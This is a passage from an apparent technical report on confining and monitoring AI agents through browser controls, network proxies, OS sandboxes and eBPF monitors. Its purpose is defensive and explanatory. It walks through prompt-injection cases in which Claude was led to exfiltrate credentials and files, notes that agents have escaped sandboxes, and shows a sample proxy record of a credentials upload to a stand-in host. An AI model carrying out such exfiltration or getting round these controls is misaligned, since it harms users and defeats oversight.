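Google's *Gemini in Chrome* lists policies that let companies control whether the agent may act on websites and which addresses to allow or block. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) reports that Chrome Enterprise's rules against transfers of sensitive data now cover agents as well as employees, and that the browser's history labels pages that an agent opened in the background. An extension cannot easily reproduce that label, because only the browser can reliably identify the pages its own agent opened.

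### WebMCP

So far, the control has had to interpret clicks and form fields. WebMCP, a proposed web standard, would give it something closer to an MCP tool call. Each page lists its tools for the agent, with a description and named arguments for each tool. The site in action (c) might offer a `submit_application` tool, which the agent would call with the applicant's name and address instead of finding the right form fields.

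Developers can create such tools by writing JavaScript or by adding annotations to an ordinary HTML form (Google, 2026). Websites can sign up to test WebMCP from Chrome 149 onwards, but the design may still change. An agent has to visit a page to learn which tools the page offers. By default, embedded frames from other sites cannot offer tools.

With WebMCP, an extension can act as a protocol control inside the browser. Google provides an inspector extension that tests a page's tools, so a security extension could plausibly check a tool's description before an agent reads it and its arguments before the call runs. This is easiest if the agent and the control are the same extension, because a separate control would have to work through the page. Search Engine Journal's *WebMCP can be used to hijack AI agents Chrome warns* quotes Chrome's warning that extensions with permission for a site can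 already manipulate its pages with their own code. However, this access does not guarantee that a built-in agent will wait for the extension's decision.

Google (2026) published security guidance for agent developers on 9 June. It covers two routes for prompt injection that also exist in MCP: a malicious site's tool definitions, and text planted in a legitimate site's tool results, for example in a user comment. Google recommends fixed limits first. The agent should reject overlong results, interact only with sites relevant to the task and ask the user to confirm actions where needed.

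Further measures depend on a model and are less predictable. Developers can mark outside text as data with delimiters or by encoding it. Delimiters add few tokens, the units of text that a model processes, but an attacker may imitate them. Base64 encoding prevents this but uses about 33% more tokens. Google also suggests using classifiers to scan tool descriptions and results, and a second model to compare each planned call with the user's request.

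In companion guidance for websites, Google (2026) asks developers to label tools that return untrusted content, tools with serious consequences and tools that only read. It advises agents to assume that a tool changes something unless its description or labels clearly state otherwise. The labels are useful if the site is honest, but a dishonest site can falsify both the labels and the description. A security extension would do better to apply MCP's stricter rule on labels, and not skip confirmation just because an unknown site labels a tool "read-only".

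### Remote debugging

Many browser agents control the browser through the Chrome DevTools Protocol, an interface for debugging web pages. *When your user is an AI agent*, a personal article by a developer of Chrome's debugging software, explains that the protocol assumes a trusted client and has no authentication of its own. A connected program can read every cookie, attach to any open tab, run code in any page and intercept network traffic.

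An extension can access only the sites and functions its permissions cover. With the `debugger` permission, it can use the parts of the Chrome DevTools Protocol that Google's *chrome.debugger* lists as available to extensions. A control could use these to monitor a tab's traffic more closely than request rules allow, but Chrome would then show a banner notifying the user that the extension is debugging the browser. UiPath's *Debugging banner notification after extension upgrade to Manifest V3* describes this banner for its own automation product.

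Criminals had also used the protocol to steal cookies. *Changes to remote debugging switches to improve security* (Harris, 2025) therefore announced that, from Chrome 136, the command-line switches for remote debugging would no longer work on the user's default profile, which stores cookies, logins and settings. A program that uses the switches has to open a separate profile, which has a different encryption key.

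Developers still wanted coding agents to work in pages where they had already logged in. Chrome 144 added a way to do this, and Google's *Let your Coding Agent debug your browser session with Chrome DevTools MCP* (2025) describes the approvals required. The developer first has to turn on remote debugging. Chrome then asks for permission each time the agent's MCP server requests a session, and shows a banner while the session lasts. The approval ends when the server disconnects or the browser restarts.

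Each approval covers everything the agent does over that connection. Google's *Connect your AI agent to your personal browser with auto-connect* warns that a connected agent can access all data in the profile, including open tabs and cookies. If the developer clicks "Allow" so that the agent can inspect a broken page, the same approval lets it submit the form in action (c). A control extension in that profile might detect the form, but the agent's connection has more power over the browser than the extension does. The extension therefore cannot be relied on as the tamper-proof check that Anderson required.

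A separate profile avoids exposing the developer's existing logins, but it starts without any extension the developer installed by hand. *Mind the Web* notes that such agents can sign in to sites during a task. If the agent does so in this profile, it acts in a logged-in session without that extension to check what it does.

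## What does decrypting network traffic add?

The script in action (b) doesn't pass through an MCP proxy or a browser extension, but it has to use the network to send the credentials anywhere. Actions (c) and (d) also use the network, so a control on the network path can cover all three without changes to the programs. Its effectiveness depends on whether all traffic has to pass through it and whether it can read the content.

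### Filtering by destination

The simplest network control checks only where a connection goes. A program connects to a numeric address and a port, usually port 443 for encrypted web traffic. It normally also names the site in its *ClientHello*, the first message of a TLS connection, so that a server hosting several sites can send the right certificate. This name is unencrypted, so a filter can compare it with an *egress allowlist*, a list of the destinations an agent may contact, and drop connections to any other destination.

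If the outside host is not on the list, the upload fails, whatever led the agent to run the script. This matters most when the model has no sign of an attack. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise in February 2026 in which a researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prompt into Claude Code. The prompt included, among ordinary setup steps, an instruction to send cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude followed it in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instruction came from the user, a classifier that checks for departures from the user's wishes had nothing to detect, but a limit on destinations would still have applied.

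A filter provides much less information about traffic to permitted destinations. Joos and Pradel note that installing a package and sending data to an attacker can both appear as a connection to some address on port 443. The size and timing of encrypted messages reveal a little more. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) reviews research that used them to infer the topics of prompts to 28 models and to identify, with an F1 score of 0.866, which agent had produced some traffic. These methods need trained models for each agent and provider, and their results are only probable. They might help a company discover agents it didn't know about, but they are a poor basis for blocking a particular upload.

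### Asking programs to use a proxy

Many programs read a proxy's address from an environment variable, a setting that a process normally inherits from the process that started it. If `HTTPS_PROXY` contains an address, a program that follows this setting connects there and requests a tunnel to the destination site. The proxy checks the site's name and then relays the data without decrypting it.

Programs can ignore the environment variable that specifies a proxy. Waldrep's *Politeness vs Enforcement* describes a coding agent on a Linux machine where this variable pointed to a scanning proxy. The agent started a subprocess to renew a login token. The subprocess did not inherit the variable, so it connected directly and renewed the token. The request did not appear in the proxy's log, and the dashboard still showed compliant traffic.

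This is one anecdote, from a post that also promotes a proxy, but Anthropic lists plain `ssh` and most database drivers among the tools that ignore these variables. A proxy that programs can bypass does not provide complete mediation, even when the bypass is unintentional.

### Forcing traffic to the proxy

The proxy is compulsory only if the operating system blocks every other route. Claude Code's optional sandbox for shell commands does this on Linux by running each command in a separate network environment with no outside connection. On macOS, it blocks connections to anything but the proxy, which runs outside the sandbox. Tools that ignore the environment variables then fail to connect.

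That is safer, but it breaks legitimate work. A database driver cannot reach even an allowed host, so the developer may exempt its command from the sandbox, which gives that command unrestricted network access. The proxy is also compulsory only for processes inside the sandbox, which does not cover Claude Code's built-in web tools or local MCP servers.

The operating system can instead redirect traffic to the proxy without the program's cooperation, so the program does not need to support proxies. Stronghold's *Why Network-Level Scanning* describes a product that does this for every process under a chosen user account. In *Kairos*, Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026) run the whole agent in a virtual machine and use a firewall rule to send all its outgoing traffic to a proxy. The proxy still has to be able to interpret the redirected traffic.

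In both designs, the proxy needs network access that the agent lacks. Waldrep recommends separate user accounts for the agent, the proxy and the developer on a developer's own machine. The firewall can then block the agent's direct connections without affecting the other two accounts. If the agent and the proxy shared an account, the firewall could not use accounts to distinguish their connections.

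### How TLS inspection works

The proxy now handles every connection but can read only the destination. To read the content, it has to become an endpoint of the encrypted connection.

Normally a website proves its identity with a certificate that ties its name to a public key. A certificate authority signs the certificate. The device stores *root certificates* for the authorities it trusts, and a program accepts the site's certificate if it matches the site's name and the signatures lead back to one of those roots. The program and the site then agree on encryption keys that no system between them has.

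For TLS inspection, a company creates its own certificate authority and adds its root certificate to the device, which requires permission to change what the device trusts. Suppose the script then tries to upload a file to `files.example`:

1. The script starts a TLS connection, and the proxy answers in place of the site.
2. The proxy creates a certificate for `files.example` and signs it with the company's authority.
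3. The script finds the right name and a signature from a trusted authority, so it accepts the certificate and agrees on encryption keys with the proxy.
4. The proxy opens a second TLS connection to the real `files.example` and checks the site's own certificate, which the script can no longer do for itself.
5. The proxy decrypts the script's request, applies its rules, and either refuses the request or encrypts it again and sends it on. Replies return the same way.

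The data is encrypted on both connections but readable inside the proxy. In simplified form, the proxy's record of the upload changes like this:

```text
Without decryption
  files.example, port 443, 4,180 bytes sent

With decryption
  POST https://files.example/upload
  Authorization: Bearer [account token]
  {"name": "credentials", "content": "..."}
```

Decrypting traffic lets a rule depend on the operation, the account or the content. For example, a rule could allow downloads from `files.example` but refuse uploads, or refuse any request that contains an access key. *Connection Escrow* (2026) avoids adding a root certificate by reading the text inside the program before encryption, but this requires a monitor in the kernel.

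### The agent's conversation with its model

When a model runs on a provider's servers, each round the harness sends it the conversation over the network. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) examines routers, which are services that sit between agents and model providers and terminate the TLS connection on each side. A router can therefore read the user's prompts, the tool definitions and outputs, any credentials in the traffic, and the tool calls the model returns. A company's decrypting proxy on the same route can read the same data.

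In the running example, the proxy would receive the developer's request, the planted text from the documentation page and the model's request to run the script. The model's request arrives before the harness acts on it, so a control could compare the proposed command with the developer's request, which mcp-context-protector could not do. This is probably the most that network inspection can do to narrow the semantic gap. However, the control would have to parse each provider's message format, and it would have access to everything the developer told the agent.

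Hempel and colleagues use a proxy that decrypts and logs traffic to the model provider but always lets it through, because they treat the provider as a trusted part of the agent.

### An approved domain and an attacker's account

In May 2026, Anthropic published a case in which data escaped from Claude Cowork, an agent for general office work, even though the destination filter worked as designed. Cowork ran in a virtual machine on the user's computer, with access to a folder the user had chosen. The filter was an egress allowlist that had to include `api.anthropic.com`, because Cowork cannot work without Anthropic's service.

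Outside researchers reported the problem. A malicious file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key, a credential for using Anthropic's service. Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the folder and used the attacker's key to upload them through Anthropic's file-storage interface. The proxy let the upload through because its destination was an approved domain. The files ended up in the attacker's Anthropic account.

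Anthropic fixed this by adding a second proxy, inside the virtual machine, that decrypts traffic to Anthropic's service. When a session starts, the virtual machine receives its own token. The proxy passes only requests that carry this token, so it rejects requests with the attacker's key. It also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something on the agent's behalf.

The new proxy's location matters because only software inside the virtual machine could detect that this session should have been using a different credential. Anthropic's servers could not, because the attacker's key was valid and a request from Cowork looks the same as one from any other customer's program.

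Anthropic used to think of the allowlist as a filter on destinations, but now describes each entry as a "capability grant". Approving a domain permits every function behind it, for every account that can use it. In the running example, an entry for the document service lets the agent read a document and share it with an outsider. An entry for `github.com` lets the agent download code and publish it. A company writing an allowlist should ask what someone could do at each domain, as well as whether it trusts the domain's owner.

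Decryption makes narrower grants possible, but someone still has to write them. The token check protects one service whose maker knows which credential each session should carry. It would not stop the agent from sharing the document through the developer's own account, because the request would carry the right credential. To block that, the proxy would need a rule about the recipient, similar to the rule on `share_document` in the MCP proxy.

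Companies can check accounts more generally if the service supports it. Anthropic lets an organisation's proxy add a header to each request with a list of permitted organisations. Anthropic then refuses requests from accounts outside those organisations, including requests that use an API key. The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to add the header, and it should overwrite any such header already in the request, since otherwise the program could supply its own list. Cato Networks' *Managing Tenant Restrictions for SaaS Apps (Tenant Restrictions Policy)* describes similar headers for ChatGPT and Microsoft 365. If a service has no such feature, the company has to recognise accounts itself.

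A decrypting proxy can also keep credentials away from the agent. In an experimental feature of Claude Code, a sandboxed command receives a placeholder instead of a secret token, and the proxy substitutes the real token only in requests to hosts approved for it. If the script in the example read a credential protected this way, it could send only the placeholder to the outside host. The feature requires Anthropic's proxy to decrypt TLS, but the proxy does not scan the rest of the content. The feature also does not work for requests with a signature that the proxy cannot recompute after changing the credential.

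### What prevents inspection

Some programs and programming languages keep their own lists of trusted authorities, so they may not use a root certificate added to the operating system. Anthropic says that Claude Code trusts both a bundled list and the operating system's, so inspection usually works without further setup. However, Claude Code cannot read the operating system's list if the developer installed it through the package manager npm with an older version of Node.js. Cisco documents a related failure in which Claude Code's extension for the Visual Studio Code editor rejected an inspection certificate that the operating system already trusted. Naming the certificate in a separate setting fixed the problem.

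These failures can be fixed, but administrators have to find them one program at a time. *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) describes how developers made such fixes in sandboxes built for agents. They added their certificate to the system's list and to those of particular programming languages, and configured common package managers to use it. Applications with their own lists still needed more work.

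Programs that use *certificate pinning* are harder to accommodate because they accept only a particular certificate or key that their developer specified. They reject the proxy's certificate even though the device trusts the company's certificate authority. According to the Beam report, strict pinning is incompatible with interception. An administrator can block such a program or exempt its traffic from decryption, but Anderson's warning applies to exempt programs.

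Some traffic does not use the protocols that inspection proxies were built for. QUIC, the transport for HTTP/3, runs over UDP, while older web traffic runs over TCP. Yuan, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *ShieldNet*, found that programs such as Claude Desktop might bypass their proxy by using QUIC, so they blocked it to make the programs fall back to TCP. Claude Code's sandbox also blocks all outgoing UDP traffic. Blocking QUIC works because most websites still support TCP. For TCP connections that don't carry web requests, Joos and Pradel's proxy can only allow or refuse the whole connection, based on its host and port.

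The name of the destination is also becoming harder to read. The standard *TLS Encrypted Client Hello* (Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, March 2026) defines a way to encrypt the ClientHello, which includes the site's name, with a key published by the server. A filter on the path may then be able to read only the name of the company that hosts the site. *Encrypted Client Hello Deployment Considerations* (Campling, Vixie and colleagues, 2026) discusses the consequences for threat detection and content filtering in companies and schools. Encryption affects a proxy less if programs knowingly use it, because they still have to send it the hostname. A proxy that receives redirected traffic gets no such request and may be unable to determine which site's certificate to imitate.

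### One point for many applications

The strongest argument for decrypting network traffic is its breadth. One decrypting proxy can handle requests from a browser, a coding agent and any script the agent writes, without cooperation from their developers. Hempel and colleagues add that a proxy does not depend on which encryption library a program uses. Their proxy took about 1.2 milliseconds per request, which is negligible compared with the time a model takes to answer.

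Yuan and colleagues tested how useful the decrypted content is. They added hidden malicious code to tools from 139 real MCP servers. The tools kept their names, descriptions and outputs but also did things such as scan the local network or send data out. Existing scanners that check tool descriptions missed nearly all of these attacks, as did models that judged the agent's transcript. ShieldNet, a small model trained to classify the network traffic from each tool call, found almost all of them.

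| ShieldNet's input | Harmless tools flagged | Balanced accuracy |
|---|---|---|
| Structured events, with decryption | 2.3% | 0.987 |
| Structured events, without decryption | 89.7% | 0.551 |
| Raw packets, without decryption | 38.5% | 0.669 |

Balanced accuracy is the average of the share of malicious tools detected and the share of harmless tools not flagged, so 0.5 is no better than chance. Without decryption, the agent's ordinary calls to its model and tools looked the same as stolen data being sent over an encrypted connection, and ShieldNet flagged almost everything. The raw-packet version did somewhat better, partly because its long records were cut off, which reduced both correct and false alarms. Exactly how much decryption helps is therefore uncertain, but neither version without it would be usable.

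The result with decryption also calls for caution, because about 95% of the test cases were malicious, whereas most tools that a company installs are presumably harmless. If one tool in a thousand were malicious, a false-alarm rate of 2.3% would produce about 23 false alarms for each real one. The test also used only attacks that were visible on the network and ran on every call, so it didn't measure detection of tools that delete local files or wait a month before acting.

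ShieldNet also raises alarms without blocking anything. In its default streaming mode, the first correct alarm came on average 5.8 seconds after the attack finished. A faster mode cut this delay to 0.4 seconds but flagged 16.5% of harmless cases. In either mode, the data would already have left by the time of the alarm. A proxy that has to prevent theft needs rules it can apply before it forwards a request.

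Hempel and colleagues' proxy, Kairos, decides whether to allow a request before forwarding it. If a request would change something on a server and the rules don't settle whether it is allowed, the proxy can hold it and send the agent a placeholder reply so that the agent can keep working. A second model later approves or refuses the request based on what the agent did next. The proxy has to decide immediately on requests that only fetch information, because the agent needs the answer.

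On AgentDojo, the set of simulated environments that Liu also used, Kairos reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 47.0% to 2.7% with GPT-4.1 as the agent. This is encouraging for Kairos's decision method but is weak evidence for network inspection. AgentDojo's tools exist only in memory, so Kairos received the tool calls directly. A real proxy would receive web requests in many formats and have to work out what each one does.

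The same difficulty limits the argument from breadth, because a proxy that receives traffic from many applications still needs separate knowledge of each service to judge what the traffic means. In the running example, the proxy could read the script's upload in (b), the submitted form in (c) and the call to the document service in (d). But the form's request might not show whether a person or an agent clicked the button, and the configuration file in (a) might never cross the network.

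### Central inspection or inspection on the device

Companies have long inspected web traffic at a central point, either in their own network or at a security provider. Central inspection gives administrators one place to change rules and collect records. It can cover a device that runs no security software if the device trusts the company's root certificate and its traffic passes through the inspection point. Cloudflare's *Modify HTTP request headers in Gateway* describes one such service, which can add a user's identity to requests or restrict which accounts people use.

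A decrypting proxy covers only the traffic routed through it. In its instructions for government customers, Anthropic warns that requests from a device off the organisation's network do not carry the account header and are not restricted. A central proxy also usually cannot tell which process made a connection, because it sees only traffic that has already left the machine. For example, it may not be able to tell a request from the developer's browser from one that the agent's script sends to the same service.

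A proxy on the device can learn from the operating system which process made each request. dope.security's *On-Device Architecture* describes a product that decrypts traffic locally, links each request to its process and sends permitted requests straight to their destination. The company argues that this avoids the delay of going through a cloud proxy and keeps the content away from a third party. It acknowledges that the product can't cover devices without its software. It also criticizes cloud proxies for having trouble with pinned certificates, but a program that pins its certificate would reject one made by a local proxy too.

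For agents, the Cowork case favours inspection on the device, because the outcome depended on which token a particular session had received. But a local proxy has to be out of the agent's control, and an administrator has to maintain it on every machine. The sandboxes in the *Beam Model Technical Report* combine local and central inspection. A component for each sandbox checks its traffic and forwards only what the policy allows. Permitted connections then go to a service shared by the whole cluster, through tunnels that carry the sandbox's identity and details of the policy, so the service can identify which sandbox sent them.

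## How does an operating-system sandbox confine an agent?

The script in action (b) opens a credentials file and then contacts the outside host. A network proxy can act only on the second step. An operating-system sandbox can stop both, because a program needs the kernel to open a file and to use the network.

Before the agent starts work, someone sets which folders its commands may write to, which files they may read and which hosts they may contact. The harness runs each command in a sandbox with these limits, and every program that the command starts inherits them. If the command or one of those programs makes a forbidden system call, the call fails, whether the model was following the developer's request, obeying planted text or making a mistake.

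The same limits apply to programs that do more than their names suggest. If `validate_patch`, the tool that secretly deleted a password file, had run in a sandbox that allowed writes only to the project folder, the deletion would have failed.

### What enforces the limits

macOS has a built-in framework called *Seatbelt*. The harness supplies a profile, which lists what a command may do, and the macOS kernel checks the command's requests against it.

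On Linux, harnesses combine several mechanisms, including *bubblewrap*, a small program that uses *namespaces*, a kernel feature that gives a process its own view of part of the system. bubblewrap can start a command with no outside network connection and a view of the file system in which most folders are read-only or missing. It sets up these restrictions, and the kernel enforces them. bubblewrap normally needs no administrator rights, but Anthropic warns that the default policy on Ubuntu 24.04 and later blocks it until someone adds an exception.

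*seccomp* is a kernel filter that allows or refuses system calls according to their type and simple arguments such as numbers. It cannot check which file a program wants to open, because the call contains only the memory address of the file's name. It is better suited to broad prohibitions, such as a ban on network connections. *Landlock*, another kernel feature, lets a process give up access to files outside certain folders, for itself and for any program it starts. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) describes Codex using Landlock for files and seccomp for the network.

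With all of these mechanisms, the command still uses the computer's own kernel, so a flaw in that kernel could let the command escape the sandbox. *gVisor* adds a second kernel that runs as an ordinary program. This second kernel handles most system calls from the processes in a container and makes only a limited set of calls to the real kernel. When Claude runs code in the claude.ai chat service, the code runs under gVisor on Anthropic's servers, never on the user's computer, and the files last only for the session.

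A full *virtual machine* has its own kernel, files and processes. A *hypervisor*, the software that shares one computer's hardware among virtual machines, enforces the boundary with help from the processor. Even a program with administrator rights inside the virtual machine would have to get past the hypervisor to escape.

Anthropic reports that gVisor, seccomp and hypervisors have been dependable across its products, and that the part that failed was a proxy it had built itself. But it has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to complete a task, with no attacker involved. A sandbox therefore has to withstand the agent's own attempts to get around it, as well as malicious code.

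### Claude Code's sandbox

Claude Code uses Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux, with an optional seccomp filter. The sandbox is off by default. Once the developer turns it on, shell commands can write to the project folder, a temporary folder and any folders the developer has added. The sandbox's proxy starts with an empty list of approved hosts, and Claude Code normally asks the developer when a command needs a new host.

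File and network limits depend on each other. As Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains, an agent with unrestricted network access could send out any secret it could read. An agent with unrestricted file access could change files that other programs rely on, and get network access that way.

Some files inside the project folder pose the same danger. Claude Code loads settings from them, including hooks, which run outside the sandbox. If a command could edit those files, it could give itself more access the next time Claude Code read them. The sandbox therefore blocks writes to them, even though the rest of the folder is writable. This helps meet Anderson's requirement that a control be tamper-proof.

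The limits on reading are much looser. By default, sandboxed commands can read almost the entire computer, including credential files. The script in the example could therefore open the credentials file, although it could not upload the contents to a host that nobody had approved. A developer or administrator can close this gap with settings like these:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
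    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false,
    "filesystem": { "denyRead": ["~/.aws"] },
    "network": { "allowedDomains": ["docs.example"] }
  }
}
```

The `denyRead` line hides a folder that holds cloud credentials. The two lines above it override defaults that let commands run outside the sandbox so that work can continue. Without `failIfUnavailable`, Claude Code runs commands unprotected if the sandbox cannot start, for instance because bubblewrap is missing. Without the other line, Claude can ask to repeat a failed command outside the sandbox. The developer usually has to approve the repeat, but if an existing rule allows the command, it runs without a prompt.

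Even with these settings, local MCP servers stay outside the sandbox and run with the developer's full access. That includes the server that reads the configuration file in action (a), and would include `validate_patch` if it ran on a local server. Claude Code's own file tools are also outside the sandbox and follow separate permission rules. To confine the servers and file tools too, the developer has to run all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's separate sandbox program.

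### Permission prompts and approval fatigue

Claude Code originally asked the developer for approval before it wrote to a file, ran a command or used the network, though it could read files freely. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of these prompts and paid less attention to each one as the number grew, a problem known as *approval fatigue*. Most of the requests may have been harmless, so the high approval rate does not prove carelessness. But a person who approves almost every request is likely to miss the rare one they should reject.

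The sandbox reduced the number of permission prompts by 84%, because Claude Code no longer had to ask about commands that stayed within the sandbox's limits. This figure comes from Anthropic's own telemetry on internal use, so it may not hold for other companies' projects. It also doesn't measure directly how many attacks the sandbox stopped, because a sandbox with no limits would need no prompts.

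Fewer prompts could still improve security if developers gave more thought to those that remain. However, Anthropic's data show that experienced users approved actions automatically about twice as often as new users, though they also interrupted the agent more often while it worked. They seem to have moved from checking each step to watching for signs of trouble, which becomes harder as agents write longer commands or work in groups.

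Anthropic also offers an *auto mode*, in which a classifier reviews actions in place of the developer. It blocked about 0.4% of harmless commands but missed about 17% of *overeager* actions, which went beyond what the user wanted. Anthropic recommends using it inside a sandbox, which still limits any actions the classifier misses.

### When the user delivers the attack

In the February 2026 exercise, the employee received the prompt in an email that looked like a colleague asking for help. Claude sent out cloud credentials in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic thinks a human contractor would have followed the same instructions.

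Claude complied in 24 of 25 runs, which shows that its compliance was not a chance result. All 25 runs used the same prompt, though, so this is not a general success rate for such attacks.

Anthropic concludes that only limits on the agent's environment work in this situation. They can block the upload and also keep the agent from accessing the credentials. Claude Code's sandbox can do both, but by default it limits only network access. Even with that limit, an employee who trusted the email might say yes if Claude Code asked whether to allow the attacker's host. An administrator can prevent this by having Claude Code refuse unapproved hosts without asking.

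### A virtual machine for Claude Cowork

Anthropic designed Cowork for office workers, who may not be able to judge a shell command, so the company wanted a boundary that was always on and did not depend on the user's approval.

The first version of Cowork ran entirely inside a virtual machine. The virtual machine could access only the user's chosen folder and Claude's settings folder. The user's stored credentials stayed outside the virtual machine. Cowork could open a folder as read-only, writable, or writable without permission to delete. Claude could still damage files in a writable folder, but the damage would stop there unless the user had connected other services.

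In the first version of Cowork, the harness also ran inside the virtual machine. In Claude Code, a process outside the sandbox decides whether to sandbox each command, so a planted instruction or a careless approval can lead that process to exempt a command. The first version of Cowork had no such process and no way to grant an exemption.

Under this design, if the virtual machine failed to start, Cowork stopped working altogether and Claude could not help with the error. Anthropic therefore moved the harness to the user's computer and left only code execution inside the virtual machine. It considers the loss of security minimal, because the virtual machine still limits the files and network available to the agent's code. However, the harness now runs outside the boundary, so users have to trust it to send code to the virtual machine.

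Anthropic also moved local MCP servers out of the virtual machine. They were harder to audit inside it, its updates could break them, and some had to work with programs on the user's computer, such as a database. Anthropic now treats them like any other software a user might install and lets administrators decide which to allow. In Cowork, as in Claude Code, a local tool like `validate_patch` would therefore run without confinement.

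The virtual machine has other limits. It keeps out the security software that companies use to monitor their computers, and although it remained intact, it did not prevent the theft of files through Anthropic's own approved domain.

### Codex and the problem of Windows

OpenAI's Codex uses much the same mechanisms but different defaults. OpenAI's *Sandbox* gives the same reason as Anthropic for confining commands, which is to reduce approval fatigue, but Codex's sandbox is on by default. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, commands also have no network access by default, and a developer who turns it on gets an unrestricted connection unless they also enable a filtering proxy.

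| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox on by default | No | Yes |
| Where sandboxed commands can write | Project and temporary folders | Project and temporary folders |
| What they can read | Almost everything | Almost everything |
| Network | Approved hosts, through a proxy | None |
| macOS | Seatbelt | Seatbelt |
| Linux | bubblewrap, optional seccomp | bubblewrap and seccomp |
| Windows, without its Linux subsystem | No sandbox | OpenAI's own sandbox |

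Some Codex commands can run outside the sandbox despite these defaults. OpenAI (2026) describes rules that let its staff's agents run common commands, such as listing proposed code changes, outside it without approval.

Windows was more difficult. Wiesen, in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*, recalls that in September 2025 Windows users had to approve nearly every command or give Codex full access. He rejected three features of Windows:

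- AppContainer suits applications that know in advance what they need, but Codex may run almost any developer tool.
- Windows Sandbox provides a disposable virtual machine, but Codex needs the developer's actual files and tools. Home editions of Windows also lack it.
- Integrity labels could have limited where Codex writes, but they would have opened the project folder to every low-trust program on the computer.

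Wiesen's first prototype did not need administrator rights. It ran each command under the developer's account, with an extra identity created for the sandbox. A write succeeded only if both the developer and the sandbox identity had permission, and the sandbox identity had it mainly for the project folder. This worked well for files, but the network limit was weak because Codex relied on changing settings to make common tools fail to connect. A program that ignored those settings could still connect.

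Windows Firewall could not block such connections for the sandboxed commands alone, because those commands ran under the developer's account. The current design therefore creates two more Windows accounts, and the firewall blocks all outgoing connections from one of them. Waldrep recommends the same separation of accounts for a network proxy.

An administrator has to approve the setup, and some companies' policies prevent it. Codex then falls back to a mode that OpenAI's *Windows* describes as weaker, which has neither the separate accounts nor the firewall rule. How reliable Codex's network limit is can therefore depend on who is allowed to administer the Windows computer.

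Microsoft has since built confinement for agents into Windows 11. Microsoft Execution Containers (MXC) became generally available in October 2026, according to eSecurity Planet's *Microsoft Execution Containers GA* (2026). A developer lists the files and network destinations that an agent needs, and MXC chooses a container to enforce the list. Microsoft's *Windows platform security for AI agents* (2026) describes two levels of confinement from the June preview. One confines a process within the user's environment, and GitHub's Copilot CLI had already adopted it. The other runs the agent under a separate account, isolated from the user's desktop and clipboard. Microsoft also planned small virtual machines for riskier work, citing research on language models' growing ability to escape sandboxes.

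### Permitted files, harmful uses

The post *Microsoft Execution Containers* gives the example of an agent that has to update a website. The agent has permission to change the site's code and to read, but not change, the production server's configuration. If it tries to edit the configuration as a shortcut, the container blocks the edit.

However, the container would not block a harmful change to the site's code, because the agent needs to write to those files. Similarly, the coding agent in the running example has to edit the project to fix the failing test, and the same permission would let it delete the test or add a security flaw. The kernel would allow all of these changes because they are writes to permitted files.

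Tighter limits help only with files that the task does not require. Ordinary work fails and developers ask for exceptions if an administrator makes the limits too tight, but the agent can misuse anything inside the sandbox if they are too loose. OpenAI warns that when Codex runs in a development container with Codex's sandbox turned off, a malicious project can steal anything in the container, including Codex's credentials.

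Developers still have to check the result for harmful edits. OpenAI advises them to save versions of the project often so they can undo changes, and to review Codex's code as they would a colleague's.

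## Can a monitor in the kernel tell permitted actions from harmful ones?

A sandbox treats a repair and an act of sabotage alike if both write to a permitted file. A monitor in the kernel receives the same file and network operations, but it can also use earlier events in the session and the user's request to judge them. Since 2025, researchers have built several such monitors for agents, mostly with a Linux facility called eBPF.

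### What eBPF can observe and block

eBPF lets an administrator load small programs into a running Linux kernel without changing the kernel's own code. Each program runs when a chosen event occurs, such as a system call. As the *eBPF Documentation* explains, only privileged processes can normally load these programs, so an agent running as an ordinary user cannot load its own.

Before each program runs, a part of the kernel called the *verifier* checks that the program will finish, won't crash the system and won't access memory outside its limits. The verifier does not check what the program is for, so a program that spies on the user could pass.

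A probe on system calls records which process opened a file, started another program or made a connection. The monitor can also track which processes start others, so it can ignore everything except the agent and its descendants. This kind of probe observes operations but does not block them.

The monitor can stop an operation through a *security hook*, a point at which the Linux kernel checks whether the operation may proceed. *LSM BPF Programs*, in the Linux kernel documentation, shows that an eBPF program attached to the hook can deny the operation by returning an error. Unlike a seccomp filter, a security hook receives the file that the kernel has found, so a rule can refer to a particular file, and the process cannot substitute another one after the check.

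A probe can also attach to an encryption library such as OpenSSL. Programs usually encrypt traffic by passing readable text to a function in such a library, and the probe copies the text just before the function encrypts it. The monitor gets much the same content as a proxy that inspects TLS, but the device doesn't need an added root certificate and the program keeps its direct connection to the server.

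The monitor first has to find the encryption function. According to the documentation for AgentSight, the monitor by Zheng and colleagues, Claude Code and programs built on Node.js have the encryption code in their own executables, so AgentSight has to look for it there. It cannot capture the model traffic of the code editor Cursor in this way.

eBPF programs have to be simple enough for the verifier to check, so they cannot look up a site's address or ask a language model for a judgement. A monitor that needs to do these things also has a *daemon*, an ordinary program that runs in the background and answers questions from the part in the kernel.

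### Connecting the model's replies to system events

Zheng and colleagues released AgentSight in August 2025 to narrow the semantic gap. Probes on the encryption functions capture the agent's conversation with its model. Other probes capture the programs it starts, the files it opens and the connections it makes. AgentSight then uses three signals to work out which events followed from which reply:

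- Process ancestry connects an event to the agent if the process responsible descends from the agent's own.
- Timing connects a reply to events in a short window after it, between 100 and 500 milliseconds long.
- Matching arguments connect a file name, web address or command in a reply to the same text in a later system call.

Each signal is incomplete. In action (b), the model's reply names the script but may not mention the credentials file or the outside host. Matching arguments would link the reply to the script's launch, and process ancestry would link the script to the file and the host. Timing is the least certain of the three, because unrelated events can happen close together and a slow script may cause harm long after the reply.

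AgentSight gives the resulting record to a second model prompted to act as a security analyst. In the experiment with the planted README, this model processed the 37 merged events, gave a high score for a likely attack and reported a mismatch between the agent's actions and its stated goal.

The other two cases involved no attacker. In one, a research agent kept repeating a web search with the wrong arguments, and the second model identified the cause as a tool error that the agent never corrected. In the other, six coding agents on the same project produced 3,153 events even after merging, and the record showed that some agents were waiting for files that others had locked.

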